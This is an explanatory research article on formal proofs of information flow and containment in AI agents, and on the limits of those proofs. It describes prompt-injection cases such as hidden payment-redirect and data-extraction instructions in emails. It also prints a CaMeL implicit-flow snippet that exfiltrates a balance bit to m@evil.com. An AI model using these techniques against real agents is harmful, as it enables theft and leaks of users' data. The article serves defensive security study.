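# Can proofs about an AI agent's observable behaviour bound its model's hidden state?

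## What separates an agent's observable behaviour from its model's hidden state?

An AI agent combines a language model with ordinary software, called the runtime, which gives the model text and carries out the actions it requests, such as searching a mailbox or scheduling a payment. Much of that text comes from strangers, so security researchers have begun to prove theorems about agents. These theorems are mostly about events that an outside observer could record, such as which emails can affect which payments. But between reading its input and producing a word, the model computes millions of numbers, called activations, that are not in such a record. The activations make up the model's hidden state. It is a separate question whether a proof about the recorded events also limits what a stranger's text does to the hidden state.

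### One model call

A language model works on tokens, which are words or fragments of words from a fixed vocabulary. It first looks up each token in a table and replaces it with a list of numbers, called the token's embedding. In the example in *An introduction to graphical tensor notation for mechanistic interpretability* (2024), the vocabulary has about 50,000 tokens and each embedding has about 768 numbers.

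The embeddings then pass through a stack of layers. Ferrando, Sarti and colleagues (2024), in *A Primer on the Inner Workings of Transformer-based Language Models*, describe the transformer, the design behind most current language models, as a series of additions. At every position in the text, each layer adds two things to the running list of numbers. Attention contributes a weighted sum of material from the current position and all earlier ones, with weights that depend on the text itself. A feed-forward network then transforms the numbers at that one position without reference to the others. With $h_i^{\ell}$ for the numbers at position $i$ after layer $\ell$, and leaving out some rescaling steps:

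$$m_i^{\ell} = h_i^{\ell-1} + \mathrm{Attn}^{\ell}(h_1^{\ell-1},\ldots,h_i^{\ell-1}), \qquad h_i^{\ell} = m_i^{\ell} + \mathrm{FFN}^{\ell}(m_i^{\ell})$$

*Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) points out that attention is the only operation in a transformer that moves information from one position to another. A sentence near the top of an email can influence a word the model produces hundreds of tokens later, but only through attention.

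After the last layer, the model multiplies the numbers at the final position by one more matrix to get a score $z_k$ for every token $k$ in the vocabulary. The softmax function turns the scores into probabilities, $p_k = e^{z_k} / \sum_j e^{z_j}$, and a random draw picks one token. That token is added to the text, and the calculation repeats until the output is complete. Anyone who fixes the random choices in advance by setting the seed can repeat a run exactly, or with only one email changed.

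Authors differ on how much "hidden state" covers. Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), in *GIF*, use it for the activations at the single position from which the next token comes, while *Shared Global and Local Geometry of Language Model Embeddings* (2025) counts the embeddings as the initial hidden states and follows them through every layer. For questions about what a text does inside a model, it is safer to use the term for all the activations, at every layer and position, because this includes changes that fade before the final position.

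The hidden state is far larger than the output. For a 1,000-token prompt, a twelve-layer model of width 768 computes more than nine million numbers, counting only each token's running list after each layer. The output at each step is one token out of 50,000, which takes at most about 15.6 bits to identify.

### One turn of an agent

A model call produces only text. *How tool use works*, part of Anthropic's documentation for its Claude models, states, "The model never runs anything on its own." The application sends the model a user's message and descriptions of the available tools. If the model requests a tool, its output names the tool and gives the arguments in a structured format. The application's code runs the tool and sends a new request containing the original messages, the model's response and the tool's result. The loop continues until the model produces a final answer or stops for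 some other reason.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (Microsoft, 2025) explain in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that the runtime keeps the conversation as a list of messages, each with a role (system, user, assistant or tool). Before every model call, it flattens the list into a single string, which is the model's context. They add that the application determines whether to execute a tool call the model has requested.

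The interface is the boundary where text goes into the model and tokens or tool calls come out. Someone who watches the runtime can record, in order, everything that crosses the interface. This record, called the trace, contains messages, tool names, arguments and results, but no activations.

### Untrusted text

In the flattened string, the user's request sits beside web pages, documents and incoming mail. Alpay and Alpay (2026), in *AgentSecBench*, represent the model's input as a single sequence that joins trusted instructions to untrusted observations. Prompt injection exploits this: an attacker plants an instruction in text the agent will read, and the model follows it as though it came from the user. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant whose CV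 contains hidden text telling the screening system to approve the candidate for interview. A database engine can keep instructions and data separate, but the article argues that a language model has no such distinction to enforce because it only predicts the next token.

*Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reported that the security company Barracuda had found such attacks in phishing emails. The emails contained hidden instructions and were designed to manipulate AI assistants as well as the people they work for.

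One common response is to mark the untrusted part of the context with delimiters or a written warning. Alpay and Alpay call this annotation and distinguish it from enforcement, in which the runtime removes the text before the model receives it or rejects a forbidden action afterwards. Annotation may well make the model less likely to obey an attacker, but the attacker's words stay in the model's input sequence.

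### A supplier's email, handled three ways

Suppose a user asks an assistant to check whether a supplier's email confirms delivery and, if so, to schedule payment. The email is untrusted text, even if the supplier is honest, because someone other than the user wrote it. It might report that forty crates reached the warehouse on Tuesday, but it might also contain an instruction, in white letters on a white background, to send the money to a new account. The user wants the report to affect the payment and the instruction to have no effect, so blocking all influence from the email would defeat the purpose of the request.

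In case A, the runtime puts the email into the context of the planner, the model call that chooses the agent's actions. The planner requests a payment, and the runtime checks the request before carrying it out. It could check the payment itself, for instance by allowing transfers only to accounts already on file, or it could check where the request came from. Costa and colleagues check where it came from, using labels that record how trusted the sources of each piece of data are. Under their policy, the runtime refuses any consequential action that the planner requests from a context containing untrusted text.

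In case B, the runtime stores the email and gives the planner only a name for it, such as `email_0`. The planner can ask the runtime to forward `email_0` to the accounts department, and the runtime fills in the text just before sending it, so no model reads the email. But the planner can't act on the "if so" in the user's request, because whether to pay depends on what the email says. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent when the same sequence of tool calls solves it whatever the data turn out to be, and they note that a planner that handles only names can solve only tasks of this kind. A person in accounts therefore has to decide whether to pay.

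In case C, a separate quarantined model reads the email. It has no tools, and the runtime lets it output only "yes", "no" or "unclear". The planner receives only that word, not the email. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) places this arrangement within the "Dual LLM" pattern, whose original version already let the planner receive restricted outputs of this kind. Two models now run on the user's behalf, each with its own hidden state, and a claim about one need not hold for the other.

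### From the email to the payment

In case A, the email affects the payment in stages. Let $X$ be the untrusted text, $H$ the planner's hidden state, $Y$ the planner's output and $A$ the action that the runtime permits (the letter has no connection with case A):

$$X \rightarrow H \rightarrow Y \rightarrow A$$

The arrows mean that each quantity depends on the earlier ones only through the one immediately before it. A sequence with this property is a Markov chain. A model call has this property if we hold the model's weights and the trusted part of the context constant and let $H$ include the activations for tokens the model has already generated. Given $H$, the only remaining randomness is in the final draw, which is independent of the email.

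The last arrow is based on the assumption that the runtime decides from $Y$ and from rules that ignore the email's wording. A runtime that also searched the email for suspicious phrases would create a second route from $X$ to $A$ that bypasses the model. Forwarding the stored email in case B also creates such a route. Case C has a longer chain, in which the email affects the quarantined model's hidden state, then its one-word answer, and only then the planner's hidden state, output and action.

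Mutual information measures how much one quantity in such a chain reveals about another. For discrete quantities the definition is

$$I(X;Y) = \sum_{x,y} p(x,y)\,\log_2 \frac{p(x,y)}{p(x)\,p(y)}$$

The fraction compares how often $x$ and $y$ occur together with how often they would if they were independent. The result is measured in bits. MIT OpenCourseWare's lecture notes *Information measures* prove that it is zero exactly when the two quantities are independent and never exceeds the entropy of either one, which is the average number of bits needed to specify its value.

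Suppose the supplier is equally likely to send a standard email confirming delivery or one denying it, and the planner outputs "pay" or "wait" to match. The output then carries 1 bit about the email. If the planner gets one in ten emails of each kind wrong, the output carries about 0.53 bits. If the runtime refuses every payment, the permitted action carries 0 bits. These figures depend on how likely each email is, which is hard to know when an attacker chooses the text. But whatever the attacker does, an answer limited to yes, no or unclear can carry at most $\log_2 3$, or about 1.58 bits. Costa and colleagues use the same reasoning to cap a yes-or-no output at 1 bit.

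The data-processing inequality says that, along a Markov chain, no later stage carries more information about the start than an earlier one does:

$$I(X;H) \;\ge\; I(X;Y) \;\ge\; I(X;A)$$

Each stage depends only on the previous one, so if a fact about the email is missing from $H$, no later stage can recover it. Venkataramanan (2015) writes in *Channel Coding Converse*, a set of Cambridge lecture slides, that processing data "cannot increase the information" about their source.

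The proof is short. One can split the information that $H$ and $Y$ jointly carry about $X$ in two ways:

$$I(X;H) + I(X;Y \mid H) \;=\; I(X;Y) + I(X;H \mid Y)$$

The bar means "given", so $I(X;Y \mid H)$ is the information $Y$ adds about the email once $H$ is known. In a Markov chain $Y$ adds nothing, so that term is zero. The last term cannot be negative, so $I(X;H)$ is at least as large as $I(X;Y)$. The same argument applies to the step from $Y$ to $A$.

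### Four things a bound could limit

A proof could "bound" the email's effect on the hidden state in several senses, and a bound in one sense does not automatically imply a bound in another.

The simplest is *dependence*, whether the hidden state changes at all. To test it in the example, one would replace the supplier's email, keep the seed and everything else the same, and check whether any activation in the planner changes. Noninterference, the property that many security proofs aim for, concerns the same yes-or-no question about what an observer sees. The two answers can differ. Xu and colleagues show a recorded model call in which the model processes two pieces of inserted text but uses only one in its output.

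A bound on *amount* limits the change to a number of bits. For case C, it would limit how many bits about the supplier's email the planner's hidden state can hold after the planner has received its one-word answer. The meaning of such a number depends on what the bits measure. In a hiring example, Štorek and colleagues estimate that an instruction hidden in a CV sends 82 bits into the agent's recommendation, compared with 27 from the trusted system prompt. Those figures measure how visible small perturbations of each passage would be in the output, which differs from the information needed to pick out one whole email among all possible emails.

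*Displacement* is the distance the planner's activations move when the input changes, for example when "Tuesday" becomes "Wednesday" in the supplier's email. For a small change in the input embeddings, multiplying by the Jacobian matrix gives the first-order change in the hidden state. Displacement can change without affecting mutual information. Dividing every activation by a thousand shrinks the displacement a thousandfold, but this is a one-to-one transformation, which the MIT OpenCourseWare notes show preserves mutual information.

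The remaining sense is *content*, or what the hidden state comes to represent. A single bit in the planner could record that the crates have arrived, or that the email's instructions now take priority over the user's. Both are the same amount of information, but only the second should worry the user. Researchers who study content often train a small classifier, called a probe, to predict a given property from the activations.

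We can now state the question exactly. Suppose the model's weights and the trusted part of the context are fixed, and let $X$ range over every text an attacker could put in the email. Suppose also that someone has proved that the trace satisfies a given condition for every $X$. In the planner and in any quarantined model, what are the tightest limits this proof implies on how $H$ depends on $X$, how much information $H$ carries about $X$, how far $H$ is displaced, and what $H$ contains?

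## What do proofs about an agent's information flow establish?

Most of the existing proofs concern noninterference or a weaker version of it. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) cites a 1982 paper by Goguen and Meseguer for the classical definition, which compares two runs of the same system that differ only in one protected input. Noninterference holds if a given observer can never tell the two runs apart, whatever values that input takes.

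### Two runs with one difference

The classical use is secrecy. Suppose the payment assistant can read the user's bank balance, and the observer is the supplier, who sees only the messages the assistant sends him. Write $s$ for the balance, $p$ for everything else that goes into the run (including the email and the seed) and $O$ for the messages the supplier receives. Noninterference then requires

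$$O(p,s) = O(p,s') \quad \text{for all } p, s, s'$$

The same comparison works for integrity, which means protection against tampering. Here the email varies, and the observer watches whatever the email is not supposed to affect, such as payments. With $x$ and $x'$ for two versions of the email, $t$ for the trusted inputs and the seed, and $A$ for the payments that the runtime permits, the requirement is

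$$A(t,x) = A(t,x') \quad \text{for all } t, x, x'$$

A secrecy proof limits what the supplier can learn about the user, but not what the supplier's email does to the agent, because the runs it compares all contain the same email. Limiting the email's effect requires an integrity proof, which compares runs in which the untrusted text varies.

No single trace can violate noninterference. A record of one £900 payment does not show what would have happened with a different email, and nobody can rerun the agent on every possible email. To enforce the property, the runtime has to check something within a single run, and most systems check labels.

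### How labels spread

In FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built, labels mark data as either trusted or untrusted, and as either public or secret. When the runtime combines two pieces of data, the result gets the join of their labels, written $\sqcup$, which is the least restrictive label that covers both:

$$\text{trusted} \sqcup \text{untrusted} = \text{untrusted}, \qquad \text{public} \sqcup \text{secret} = \text{secret}$$

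Labels can also be sets of people. If Ana and Ben may have written one document, and Ben and Chloe another, then any of the three may have contributed to a text that combines them. If the same labels instead list who is allowed to read each document, only Ben is allowed to read the combined text.

Model calls are the hard case. Ordinary code that copies a date out of an email uses the date and nothing else, so the runtime can label the copy accurately. In a model call, any part of the context may have affected the output, and the runtime can't tell which parts did. Costa and colleagues therefore give the output the join of the labels on everything the model received. For a context made of messages $m_1, \ldots, m_n$ and tool descriptions $T$, the label of the output $Y$ is

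$$\ell(Y) = \ell(m_1) \sqcup \cdots \sqcup \ell(m_n) \sqcup \ell(T)$$

They describe this rule as sound but possibly too conservative. Once an untrusted email enters a conversation, the rule labels everything the model produces afterwards in that conversation as untrusted, even a word-for-word repetition of the user's request. An output can therefore be labelled untrusted even if the email had no influence on it. Some researchers have tried to narrow the label by working out which messages influenced the response.

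Under the rule, the planner's request to pay in case A inherits the untrusted label of the supplier's email, so the policy blocks the request whether the email contains a hidden instruction or just a delivery note.

In case B the planner receives only the name `email_0`, so its context and its request to forward the email stay trusted. The body of the forwarded message is untrusted. FIDES tracks the two labels separately, so a policy can require a trusted recipient while accepting an untrusted message.

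In case C the quarantined model's answer is untrusted because the model read the email, and the planner's context becomes untrusted as soon as it receives the answer. Under the rule so far, the payment should fail, as in case A. To avoid this, Costa and colleagues add the type of the data to its label. They rank types by how much information each can carry, from yes-or-no values, through choices from a fixed list, to free text. A policy can then allow a payment request that depends on an untrusted choice among three words but refuse one that depends on untrusted free text. If the amount also has to come from the email, the planner can have the quarantined model extract it into a second variable. The planner then passes that variable to the payment tool by name, without reading the amount.

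They justify this exception by arguing that a yes-or-no value alone is unlikely to carry a successful prompt injection. That is a plausible judgement about how models behave, but no theorem supports it.

### What FIDES proves

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes FIDES as having a noninterference theorem for one specific agent loop. The developer can supply any tools, but the loop that alternates between model and tools is fixed. Such a loop could satisfy the property for integrity because, as long as the planner's context is trusted, two runs that differ only in the contents of hidden variables give the planner's model the same string. Costa and colleagues represent the model as a deterministic function from messages and tool descriptions to a tool call or a reply, so the same input always produces the same output.

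For secrecy they prove something weaker, called explicit secrecy. The observer sees every public value that the tools write to a shared datastore. Let $g$ be the combined effect on the datastore of one particular sequence of steps that the agent can take. Explicit secrecy requires, for two datastores $d_1$ and $d_2$ with the same public contents,

$$d_1 =_{\text{public}} d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_{\text{public}} g(d_2)$$

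This rules out copying a secret into a public place, but an observer may still infer something about the secret from which sequence of actions the agent took. For example, an agent passes the test even if it writes "hello" to the supplier only when the user's balance is above £10,000. The message is the same whatever the balance, but the supplier learns something about the balance by receiving it. Costa and colleagues chose this weaker property deliberately. They argue that full noninterference for secrets would in effect forbid any publicly visible tool call after any call that might read a secret.

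They also tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with planted injections. With policies on, the benchmark recorded three successful attacks, but the team inspected them by hand and judged that none had really succeeded. The policies reduced the share of banking tasks completed when there were no attacks. A basic planner completed 98.8% without policies and 37.5% with them, while FIDES with policies completed 52.5%. The tests did not include outputs restricted to a fixed type, so they provide no evidence about the exception that case C depends on.

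### Two leaks in CaMeL

CaMeL, by Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, goes further than FIDES in that its planner writes a program from the user's request before anything untrusted arrives, so the control structure can be different for every request. An interpreter runs the program, labels each value and checks a policy before each tool call, while a quarantined model reads the untrusted text. Nobody has published a proof that the labels are correct, and Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL's designers call formalisation a "crucial direction" for later work.

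Garby and colleagues found two places where the tracking stops too early. In the first, an attacker wants to know whether an account balance exceeds some threshold. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email directly under that condition. But the attacker can split the condition over two variables, using a trick known since the 1970s:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
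if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to False and marks it secret. The assignment on the fourth line does not execute, and CaMeL raises labels only on a branch that executes, so `rich` remains True and public. The last line depends only on a public value, so the email goes out. If the balance is low, `tmp` stays True and public, `rich` becomes False, and no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is high. The labels in each run look reasonable, and the leak appears only when the two runs are compared.

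The second leak is outside the interpreter. When a program fails, an ordinary Python loop, which has no labels, calls the planner again. Whether the policy blocked an attempt may depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. Most information-flow systems allow one such bit per run. Here the loop can repeat the attempt with a new threshold each time, so twenty attempts would determine a balance between zero and a million pounds to the nearest pound. To reduce this leak, CaMeL censors the error messages it passes back, but without a formal guarantee.

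Both leaks involve secrets, but integrity labels have the same weakness. If a tracker ignores branches that do not execute, an untrusted email can determine the value of a variable that the runtime labels as trusted.

### A theorem for every program in a language

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, to rule out this kind of mistake. Every value in it has a label, which is updated at every step of execution. LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language of functions, with commands that add a message to a conversation with a model, receive the reply, copy the conversation or clear it. The conversation's label is the join of the labels on everything sent to it. A reply can be program code, which runs under the label of the conversation that produced it.

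A quarantined model no longer has to be built into the architecture. A few lines of code can copy the conversation, clear the copy, send it the email and return its answer, while the main conversation keeps its trusted label.

LLMbda deals with the unexecuted branch by stopping any run in which a branch that depends on a secret would write to a public conversation. In one example, a program sends the model a message that $x$ is false and then, only if a secret is true, a second message that $x$ is true. If the interpreter raised the conversation's label on the second message instead of stopping, the conversation would be labelled secret in one run and public in the other, so the label would reveal the secret. Stopping can still reveal one bit, but a retry loop written in LLMbda is part of the labelled program, so an attacker can't use it to collect one bit after another.

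Models choose their replies at random, so the theorem compares probabilities. The observer has a clearance $m$ and sees only values whose label is at or below it. Take two starting points that look the same to this observer, and let $\mu(q)$ and $\nu(q)$ be the probabilities that each run finishes with a result that looks like $q$. These can add up to less than 1, because a run may continue forever or stop at a failed check. Garby and colleagues prove that there is always a third set of probabilities $\omega$ with

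$$\mu(q) \le \omega(q), \qquad \nu(q) \le \omega(q), \qquad \sum_q \omega(q) \le 1$$

Suppose the assistant finishes with "pay" in 90% of runs after one email and in 80% after another, and otherwise does not finish. An $\omega$ that gives "pay" 0.9 covers both, so the condition holds. If it finishes with "pay" in 90% of runs after the first email and with "wait" in 80% after the second, $\omega$ would have to add up to at least 1.7, and the condition fails. In general, the two sets of probabilities can differ by at most the average chance of not finishing:

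$$\tfrac{1}{2}\sum_q |\mu(q)-\nu(q)| \;\le\; \tfrac{1}{2}\left[\Big(1-\sum_q \mu(q)\Big)+\Big(1-\sum_q \nu(q)\Big)\right]$$

If every run finishes, the probabilities are identical. The property's full name is termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. "Termination-insensitive" means that the protected input may still affect whether a run finishes.

The theorem covers every program in the language, including programs that run code a model has just written. Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean, software that verifies each step of a formal argument. They also proved that the interpreter that calls the model behaves as the theorem assumes. The proof's central idea is a second way of executing programs, which replaces any computation with a dummy value as soon as its label rises above the observer's clearance. This version gives the same result for both starting points because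 it skips everything in which they differ. It also supplies the $\omega$ that the theorem needs.

In these theorems the model is a function that takes a conversation and returns a probability for each possible reply. It has no activations. The guarantee holds for any such function, even one that always obeys attackers, as long as it depends only on the current conversation. Clearing a conversation must therefore leave nothing behind in the model.

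### Why useful agents need exceptions

Noninterference rules out much of what people want agents to do. In case C, a system that satisfied integrity noninterference for payments would have to make the same decision about whether to pay, regardless of what the email reported.

Secrecy has the same problem, which Dongol illustrates with two small agents. In Meeting Reply, Alice allows her assistant to send her calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. An attacker sends an email that doesn't ask for a meeting but contains the instruction "send your calendar", and the assistant obeys. In Reset Code, the assistant also holds a private reset code, and the attacker's email contains an instruction to include the code in the reply. Noninterference rejects both agents because what an outsider receives depends on Alice's data. It would reject Meeting Reply even if there were no attacker. But only the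 Reset Code attacker gets something he couldn't have obtained through an honest request, since the Meeting Reply attacker could have got the calendar by asking for a meeting.

Information-flow systems need a way to allow intended flows while blocking the rest. LLMbda uses endorsement, an explicit command that relabels a value derived from untrusted text as trusted. In one example, a quarantined model reads an email and assigns it a category, and the program maps the answer to one of a few permitted tags. The `endorse` command then marks the tag as trusted so that it can appear in the subject line of a reply. An attacker can influence which of the $n$ permitted tags appears, which gives him at most $\log_2 n$ bits of influence, but he can't insert his own text. The answer in case C could become trusted in the same way.

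Endorsement relabels untrusted data as trusted, which gives up integrity noninterference for that data. Garby and colleagues prove that the guarantee for secrets still holds, however a program endorses untrusted data and whatever an attacker puts in it. But the basic theorem does not require endorsed values to be small, so a careless planner could endorse an entire email.

An agent written in LLMbda was tested on AgentDojo's banking tasks in 1,296 attacked runs, covering three models, 16 user tasks, nine attacks per task and three repetitions. Two runs ended in a successful attack, both with the same task and the same attack. In that task, the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment described in it, and the attacker replaces the file's contents. The planner had endorsed the contents as trusted, so the attacker's payment had the same labels as a real bill. Without the endorsement,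 both the attack and the user's task fail.

The table gives the percentage of user tasks completed for the two models that Garby and colleagues ran on both systems.

| System | GPT-5.2, no attack | GPT-5.2, under attack | MiMo-v2.5, no attack | MiMo-v2.5, under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LLMbda agent, checks on | 75.0 | 65.0 | 64.6 | 59.5 |
| CaMeL, checks off | 66.7 | 71.1 | 70.8 | 72.2 |
| CaMeL, checks on | 37.5 | 30.0 | 37.5 | 41.5 |

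The LLMbda agent completes about as many tasks as CaMeL does with its checks turned off, and far more than CaMeL does with them on. The comparison is not quite fair, because the LLMbda agent enforces only some of CaMeL's policies. The margins of error are also wide, around 20 percentage points either way in the runs without attacks, because there are only 16 user tasks.

The two-in-1,296 figure is weaker evidence for the theorem than it looks. In about two-thirds of the task-attack pairs, the attack needs a tool that never appears in a plan written before the agent reads anything untrusted, so it would fail even without labels. With its checks off, CaMeL let through only 5 attacks in the 622 runs that finished. The case for LLMbda rests mainly on its proof, which also covers attacks that no benchmark contains.

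### Relative security

Dongol allows intended flows by comparing the agent with an imaginary reference agent, which follows the same plan under the same runtime checks but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is relatively secure if, whenever an attacker can tell two secrets apart by observing it, some attacker input would also make them distinguishable in the reference agent. Meeting Reply passes because a real meeting request makes the reference agent send the calendar too. Reset Code fails because no email makes the reference agent send the code. The plan determines which disclosures are permitted, so nobody has to list them.

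The definition permits more disclosure than it first appears to. Suppose an assistant answers a single guess about the user's balance with "right" or "wrong", and an injection makes it send the whole balance. For any two balances, a guess equal to one of them would tell them apart in the reference agent, so the injected disclosure counts as relatively secure. It fails a stricter version that Dongol also defines, in which the reference agent's input may depend on the attacker's real input but not on the secrets.

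LLMbda allows any distribution over replies, whereas Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, describes only how a model may disobey its plan. The attacker chooses which texts the model treats as instructions, what each instruction makes it do, and at which steps it obeys. An injected call can use anything in the agent's memory, including secrets. But the schedule for obeying must be fixed in advance, so the framework doesn't cover a model whose obedience depends on a secret. A real model may well behave like that, since its context can contain both the secret and the email.

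There are also three kinds of observer. An event-level observer sees the contents and order of the calls that reach them, a step-level observer also sees their timing, and a third kind can see which requests the runtime refuses. In one agent, Alice approves the exact wording of a reply, and an injection tries to send a private value in its place. The runtime allows the call only if the private value equals the approved reply. An event-level observer sees the same single message whether or not the two match, but a step-level observer sees it arrive one step earlier when they match, and so learns that they match.

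PlanTERS's main positive result concerns a fence, a rule that withdraws certain tools when the agent first reads untrusted text. If the fence withdraws every tool that an injection could call, nothing restores those tools, and each injection makes a single call, then every plan is relatively secure against an event-level observer. But the fence can also stop the agent from doing its task. In the supplier example, it would withdraw the payment tool just before the agent needed it. Relative security would not measure this loss, because the reference agent loses the tool too.

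Dongol worked through 25 example agents in Isabelle/HOL, another proof checker, in about 31,600 lines. Ten are secure and nine leak. The verdict on the other six depends on what the observer sees or on further assumptions about the attack or the model. A verdict of "secure" often covers only the attack in the example. One of the nine that leak is close to case C. A quarantined model reads both an untrusted text and the user's private notes, and the plan sends out a 1 or a 0 depending on the model's answer. Both numbers are public constants, so they pass a check whose labels track data but not decisions. An injection can still make the answer depend on the notes, so the number sent reveals something about them.

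Much of the supplier example is outside the scope of these proofs. They do not apply to Case A, because its planner chooses each call after reading the email, so a reference agent has no fixed plan to follow. PlanTERS also covers only leaks. An instruction to send the user's money to a new account can succeed without revealing any secret, and Dongol explicitly excludes this kind of hijacking. The proofs always compare two runs that contain the same email, so even a "secure" verdict does not limit how a different email would have changed the agent's actions.

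## Why do formal models stop at the model's interface?

FIDES, LLMbda and PlanTERS all describe the model without its activations, partly because many proofs about actions don't need them. The clearest example is a proof that assumes almost nothing about the model.

### A procedure with no body

Moon and Varshney (2026), in *Containment Verification*, proved a theorem about an agent's runtime in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof checker. In their code, the model is a procedure that has inputs and a type of output but no instructions. Without a technical condition on the inputs, it reads:

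```
method GetActionFromLLM(c: Constants, v: Variables)
  returns (action: Action)
```

The type `Action` lists the kinds of request the agent can make, such as reading a file or calling a tool, together with their arguments. Because the procedure has no body, Dafny must allow for it returning any value of that type, which verification researchers call havoc semantics. The rest of the program must therefore be safe whether the request comes from a well-behaved model, a hijacked one or a random number generator.

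Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, a small framework for building agents, through an interface with four kinds of action. Their policy allows the agent to read files only inside a workspace folder, call only tools on an approved list, and take only a limited number of steps. Suppose the planner follows an instruction in the supplier's email and requests a password file stored outside the workspace. The runtime rejects the request, and no file is read. The proof covers this case without explaining why the planner made the request.

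The proof compares a detailed description of the runtime with a simpler one whose safety is easier to establish, a technique known as refinement. Let $s_I$ be a state of the detailed description and $s_M$ a state of the simple one. Let $a$ be the action the model requests, and let $e_I$ and $e_M$ be the events that follow in each, such as a file being read or nothing happening. Moon and Varshney show that the two descriptions start in matching states, written $s_M \sim s_I$, and that every step preserves the match:

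$$s_M \sim s_I,\quad s_I \xrightarrow{\,a,\,e_I\,} s_I' \quad\Rightarrow\quad \text{for some } s_M', e_M:\quad s_M \xrightarrow{\,a,\,e_M\,} s_M',\quad s_M' \sim s_I'$$

The events must also match, and the detailed step must obey the policy whenever the simple step does. For any run of the detailed description, one can then build a parallel run of the simple description, step by step, from the same actions. The simple run obeys the policy whatever those actions are, so the detailed run does too. The model appears in this argument only as a sequence of actions $a_0, a_1, \ldots$, and the argument works for every sequence.

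The theorem concerns events in a description of the runtime. To turn it into a claim about the world, Moon and Varshney assume effect exclusivity, which means that every external effect available to the agent passes through the typed interface and appears as one of the modelled events. A tool that opened its own network connection or a bug in the operating system would break this assumption. They also trust, without proof, that the code converting the model's raw text into an `Action` produces a value of that type.

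The choice of actions available to the agent matters as much as the proof. If one action is "run this shell command", the policy has to cover everything a shell can do. A short list of narrow actions allows a much stronger guarantee, so whoever designs the interface is responsible for keeping the actions few and narrow.

### Proofs that compare two runs

A procedure with no body is too unpredictable for a noninterference proof. It could return "pay" in one run and "wait" in the other even if both runs gave it the same context. The property would then fail in any runtime that let the model decide on payments, however carefully the runtime hid the email. A proof that compares runs therefore needs one assumption about the model, that the same inputs and random choices lead to the same output.

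Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026), in *PerMIT*, make this assumption for a system that protects an agent's long-term memory from planted text. The planner receives untrusted memories only as names, much like `email_0` in case B. To read one, it needs an approval at a confirmation gate, where a person or a verifying model sees the exact text and accepts or rejects it. Jiang and colleagues model the planner as a strategy $P$ that chooses its next operation from three things:

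$$\text{operation}_{k+1} = P(\text{history}_k,\ \text{view}_k,\ \omega)$$

The history contains the planner's earlier operations and the replies to them. The view contains the trusted memories and anything else the runtime shows the planner, and $\omega$ stands for the random choices. The strategy can be any function, including one that helps the attacker. The formal definitions include an internal state for the planner, but Jiang and colleagues treat it as "an abbreviation for that history". Two runs with the same history therefore have the same internal state by definition, so there is nothing further to prove about that state.

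Their main theorem on this point, Reasoning Integrity, compares two runs, $\rho_1$ and $\rho_2$, with the same user input and random choices but arbitrarily different untrusted memories:

$$\mathrm{DT}(\rho_1) = \mathrm{DT}(\rho_2) \;\Rightarrow\; \mathrm{Beh}(\rho_1) = \mathrm{Beh}(\rho_2)$$

DT is the display transcript, which records everything the runtime displayed for selection or approval and every decision made in response. Beh is the sequence of the planner's operations, tool calls and replies. By the theorem, if a planted memory changes what the planner does, something in the transcript must also have changed. Jiang and colleagues checked this in Lean for a single user. Despite its name, the theorem concerns behaviour, and the runtime never inspects the planner's reasoning.

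*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026), a preprint from a consultancy, treats the model as an adversary. A skill is a package of written instructions and scripts that an agent loads to perform a task. The scripts are ordinary programs, so an analyser can work out the largest set of effects they could have. Metere writes of the model, A, "We do not model A's internal state", and assumes that its choices are unpredictable and limited only by the form of its tool calls.

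Metere also derives a limit in bits. If a skill declares $d$ capabilities, such as reading files or using the network, the runtime assigns each tool call to one of them or refuses it. The choice of capability therefore carries at most $\log_2(d+1)$ bits per call, or about 3.5 bits for ten capabilities. This limit doesn't cover the call's arguments, which can carry thousands of bits if one of them is the body of an email.

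### Reasons to leave the inside out

Companies replace the models behind their agents often, and a proof about one model's activations would have to be redone each time. A proof over all outputs avoids this. Baheri and Wei (2026), in *Controller-Agnostic Runtime Safety Certificates for Tool-Using AI Agents via Data-Driven Robust Reachability*, place a filter between the model and its tools. The filter lists the permitted actions $D(s)$ in each state $s$, where a state is a short list of facts such as whether the agent can write to a folder. With $P(s' \mid s,a)$ for the probability that action $a$ leads to state $s'$, the worst possible risk of irreversible harm within $k$ steps is

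$$V_k(s) = \max_{a \in D(s)} \sum_{s'} P(s' \mid s,a)\, V_{k-1}(s')$$

Here $V$ is 1 once harm has happened, 0 once the agent has safely stopped, and 0 in any other state when no steps remain. The maximum replaces the model's choice of action. Baheri and Wei prove that no model can have a higher probability of causing harm than one that chooses the most dangerous permitted action at every step, even if it bases its choices on the conversation so far. If that action has a 1% chance of causing harm and otherwise changes nothing, three steps carry a risk of at most $1 - 0.99^3$, or about 3%.

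The probabilities are unknown in practice, so Baheri and Wei estimate them from logs and use the most pessimistic values consistent with the data. They write that the resulting certificate "belongs to the interface, not the model". They tested one filter with seven controllers and recorded no unsafe outcomes in 1,050 episodes.

Because a worst-case bound does not depend on the model, it is the same for a careful model and a hijacked one, and a better model does not lower it. The bound also assumes that the environment responds to an action in the same way no matter who or what chose it. A file system meets this assumption if the description of the action includes everything relevant, such as the file's path. A person who reads the agent's messages is harder to model this way, because what they do next may depend on the exact wording.

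Closed weights are a more practical reason. A company that uses a model through a provider's service typically sends text and gets text back, so it has no activations to reason about. But this can't be the whole explanation, because Baheri and Wei built six of their seven controllers on models with open weights and still treated those models as opaque.

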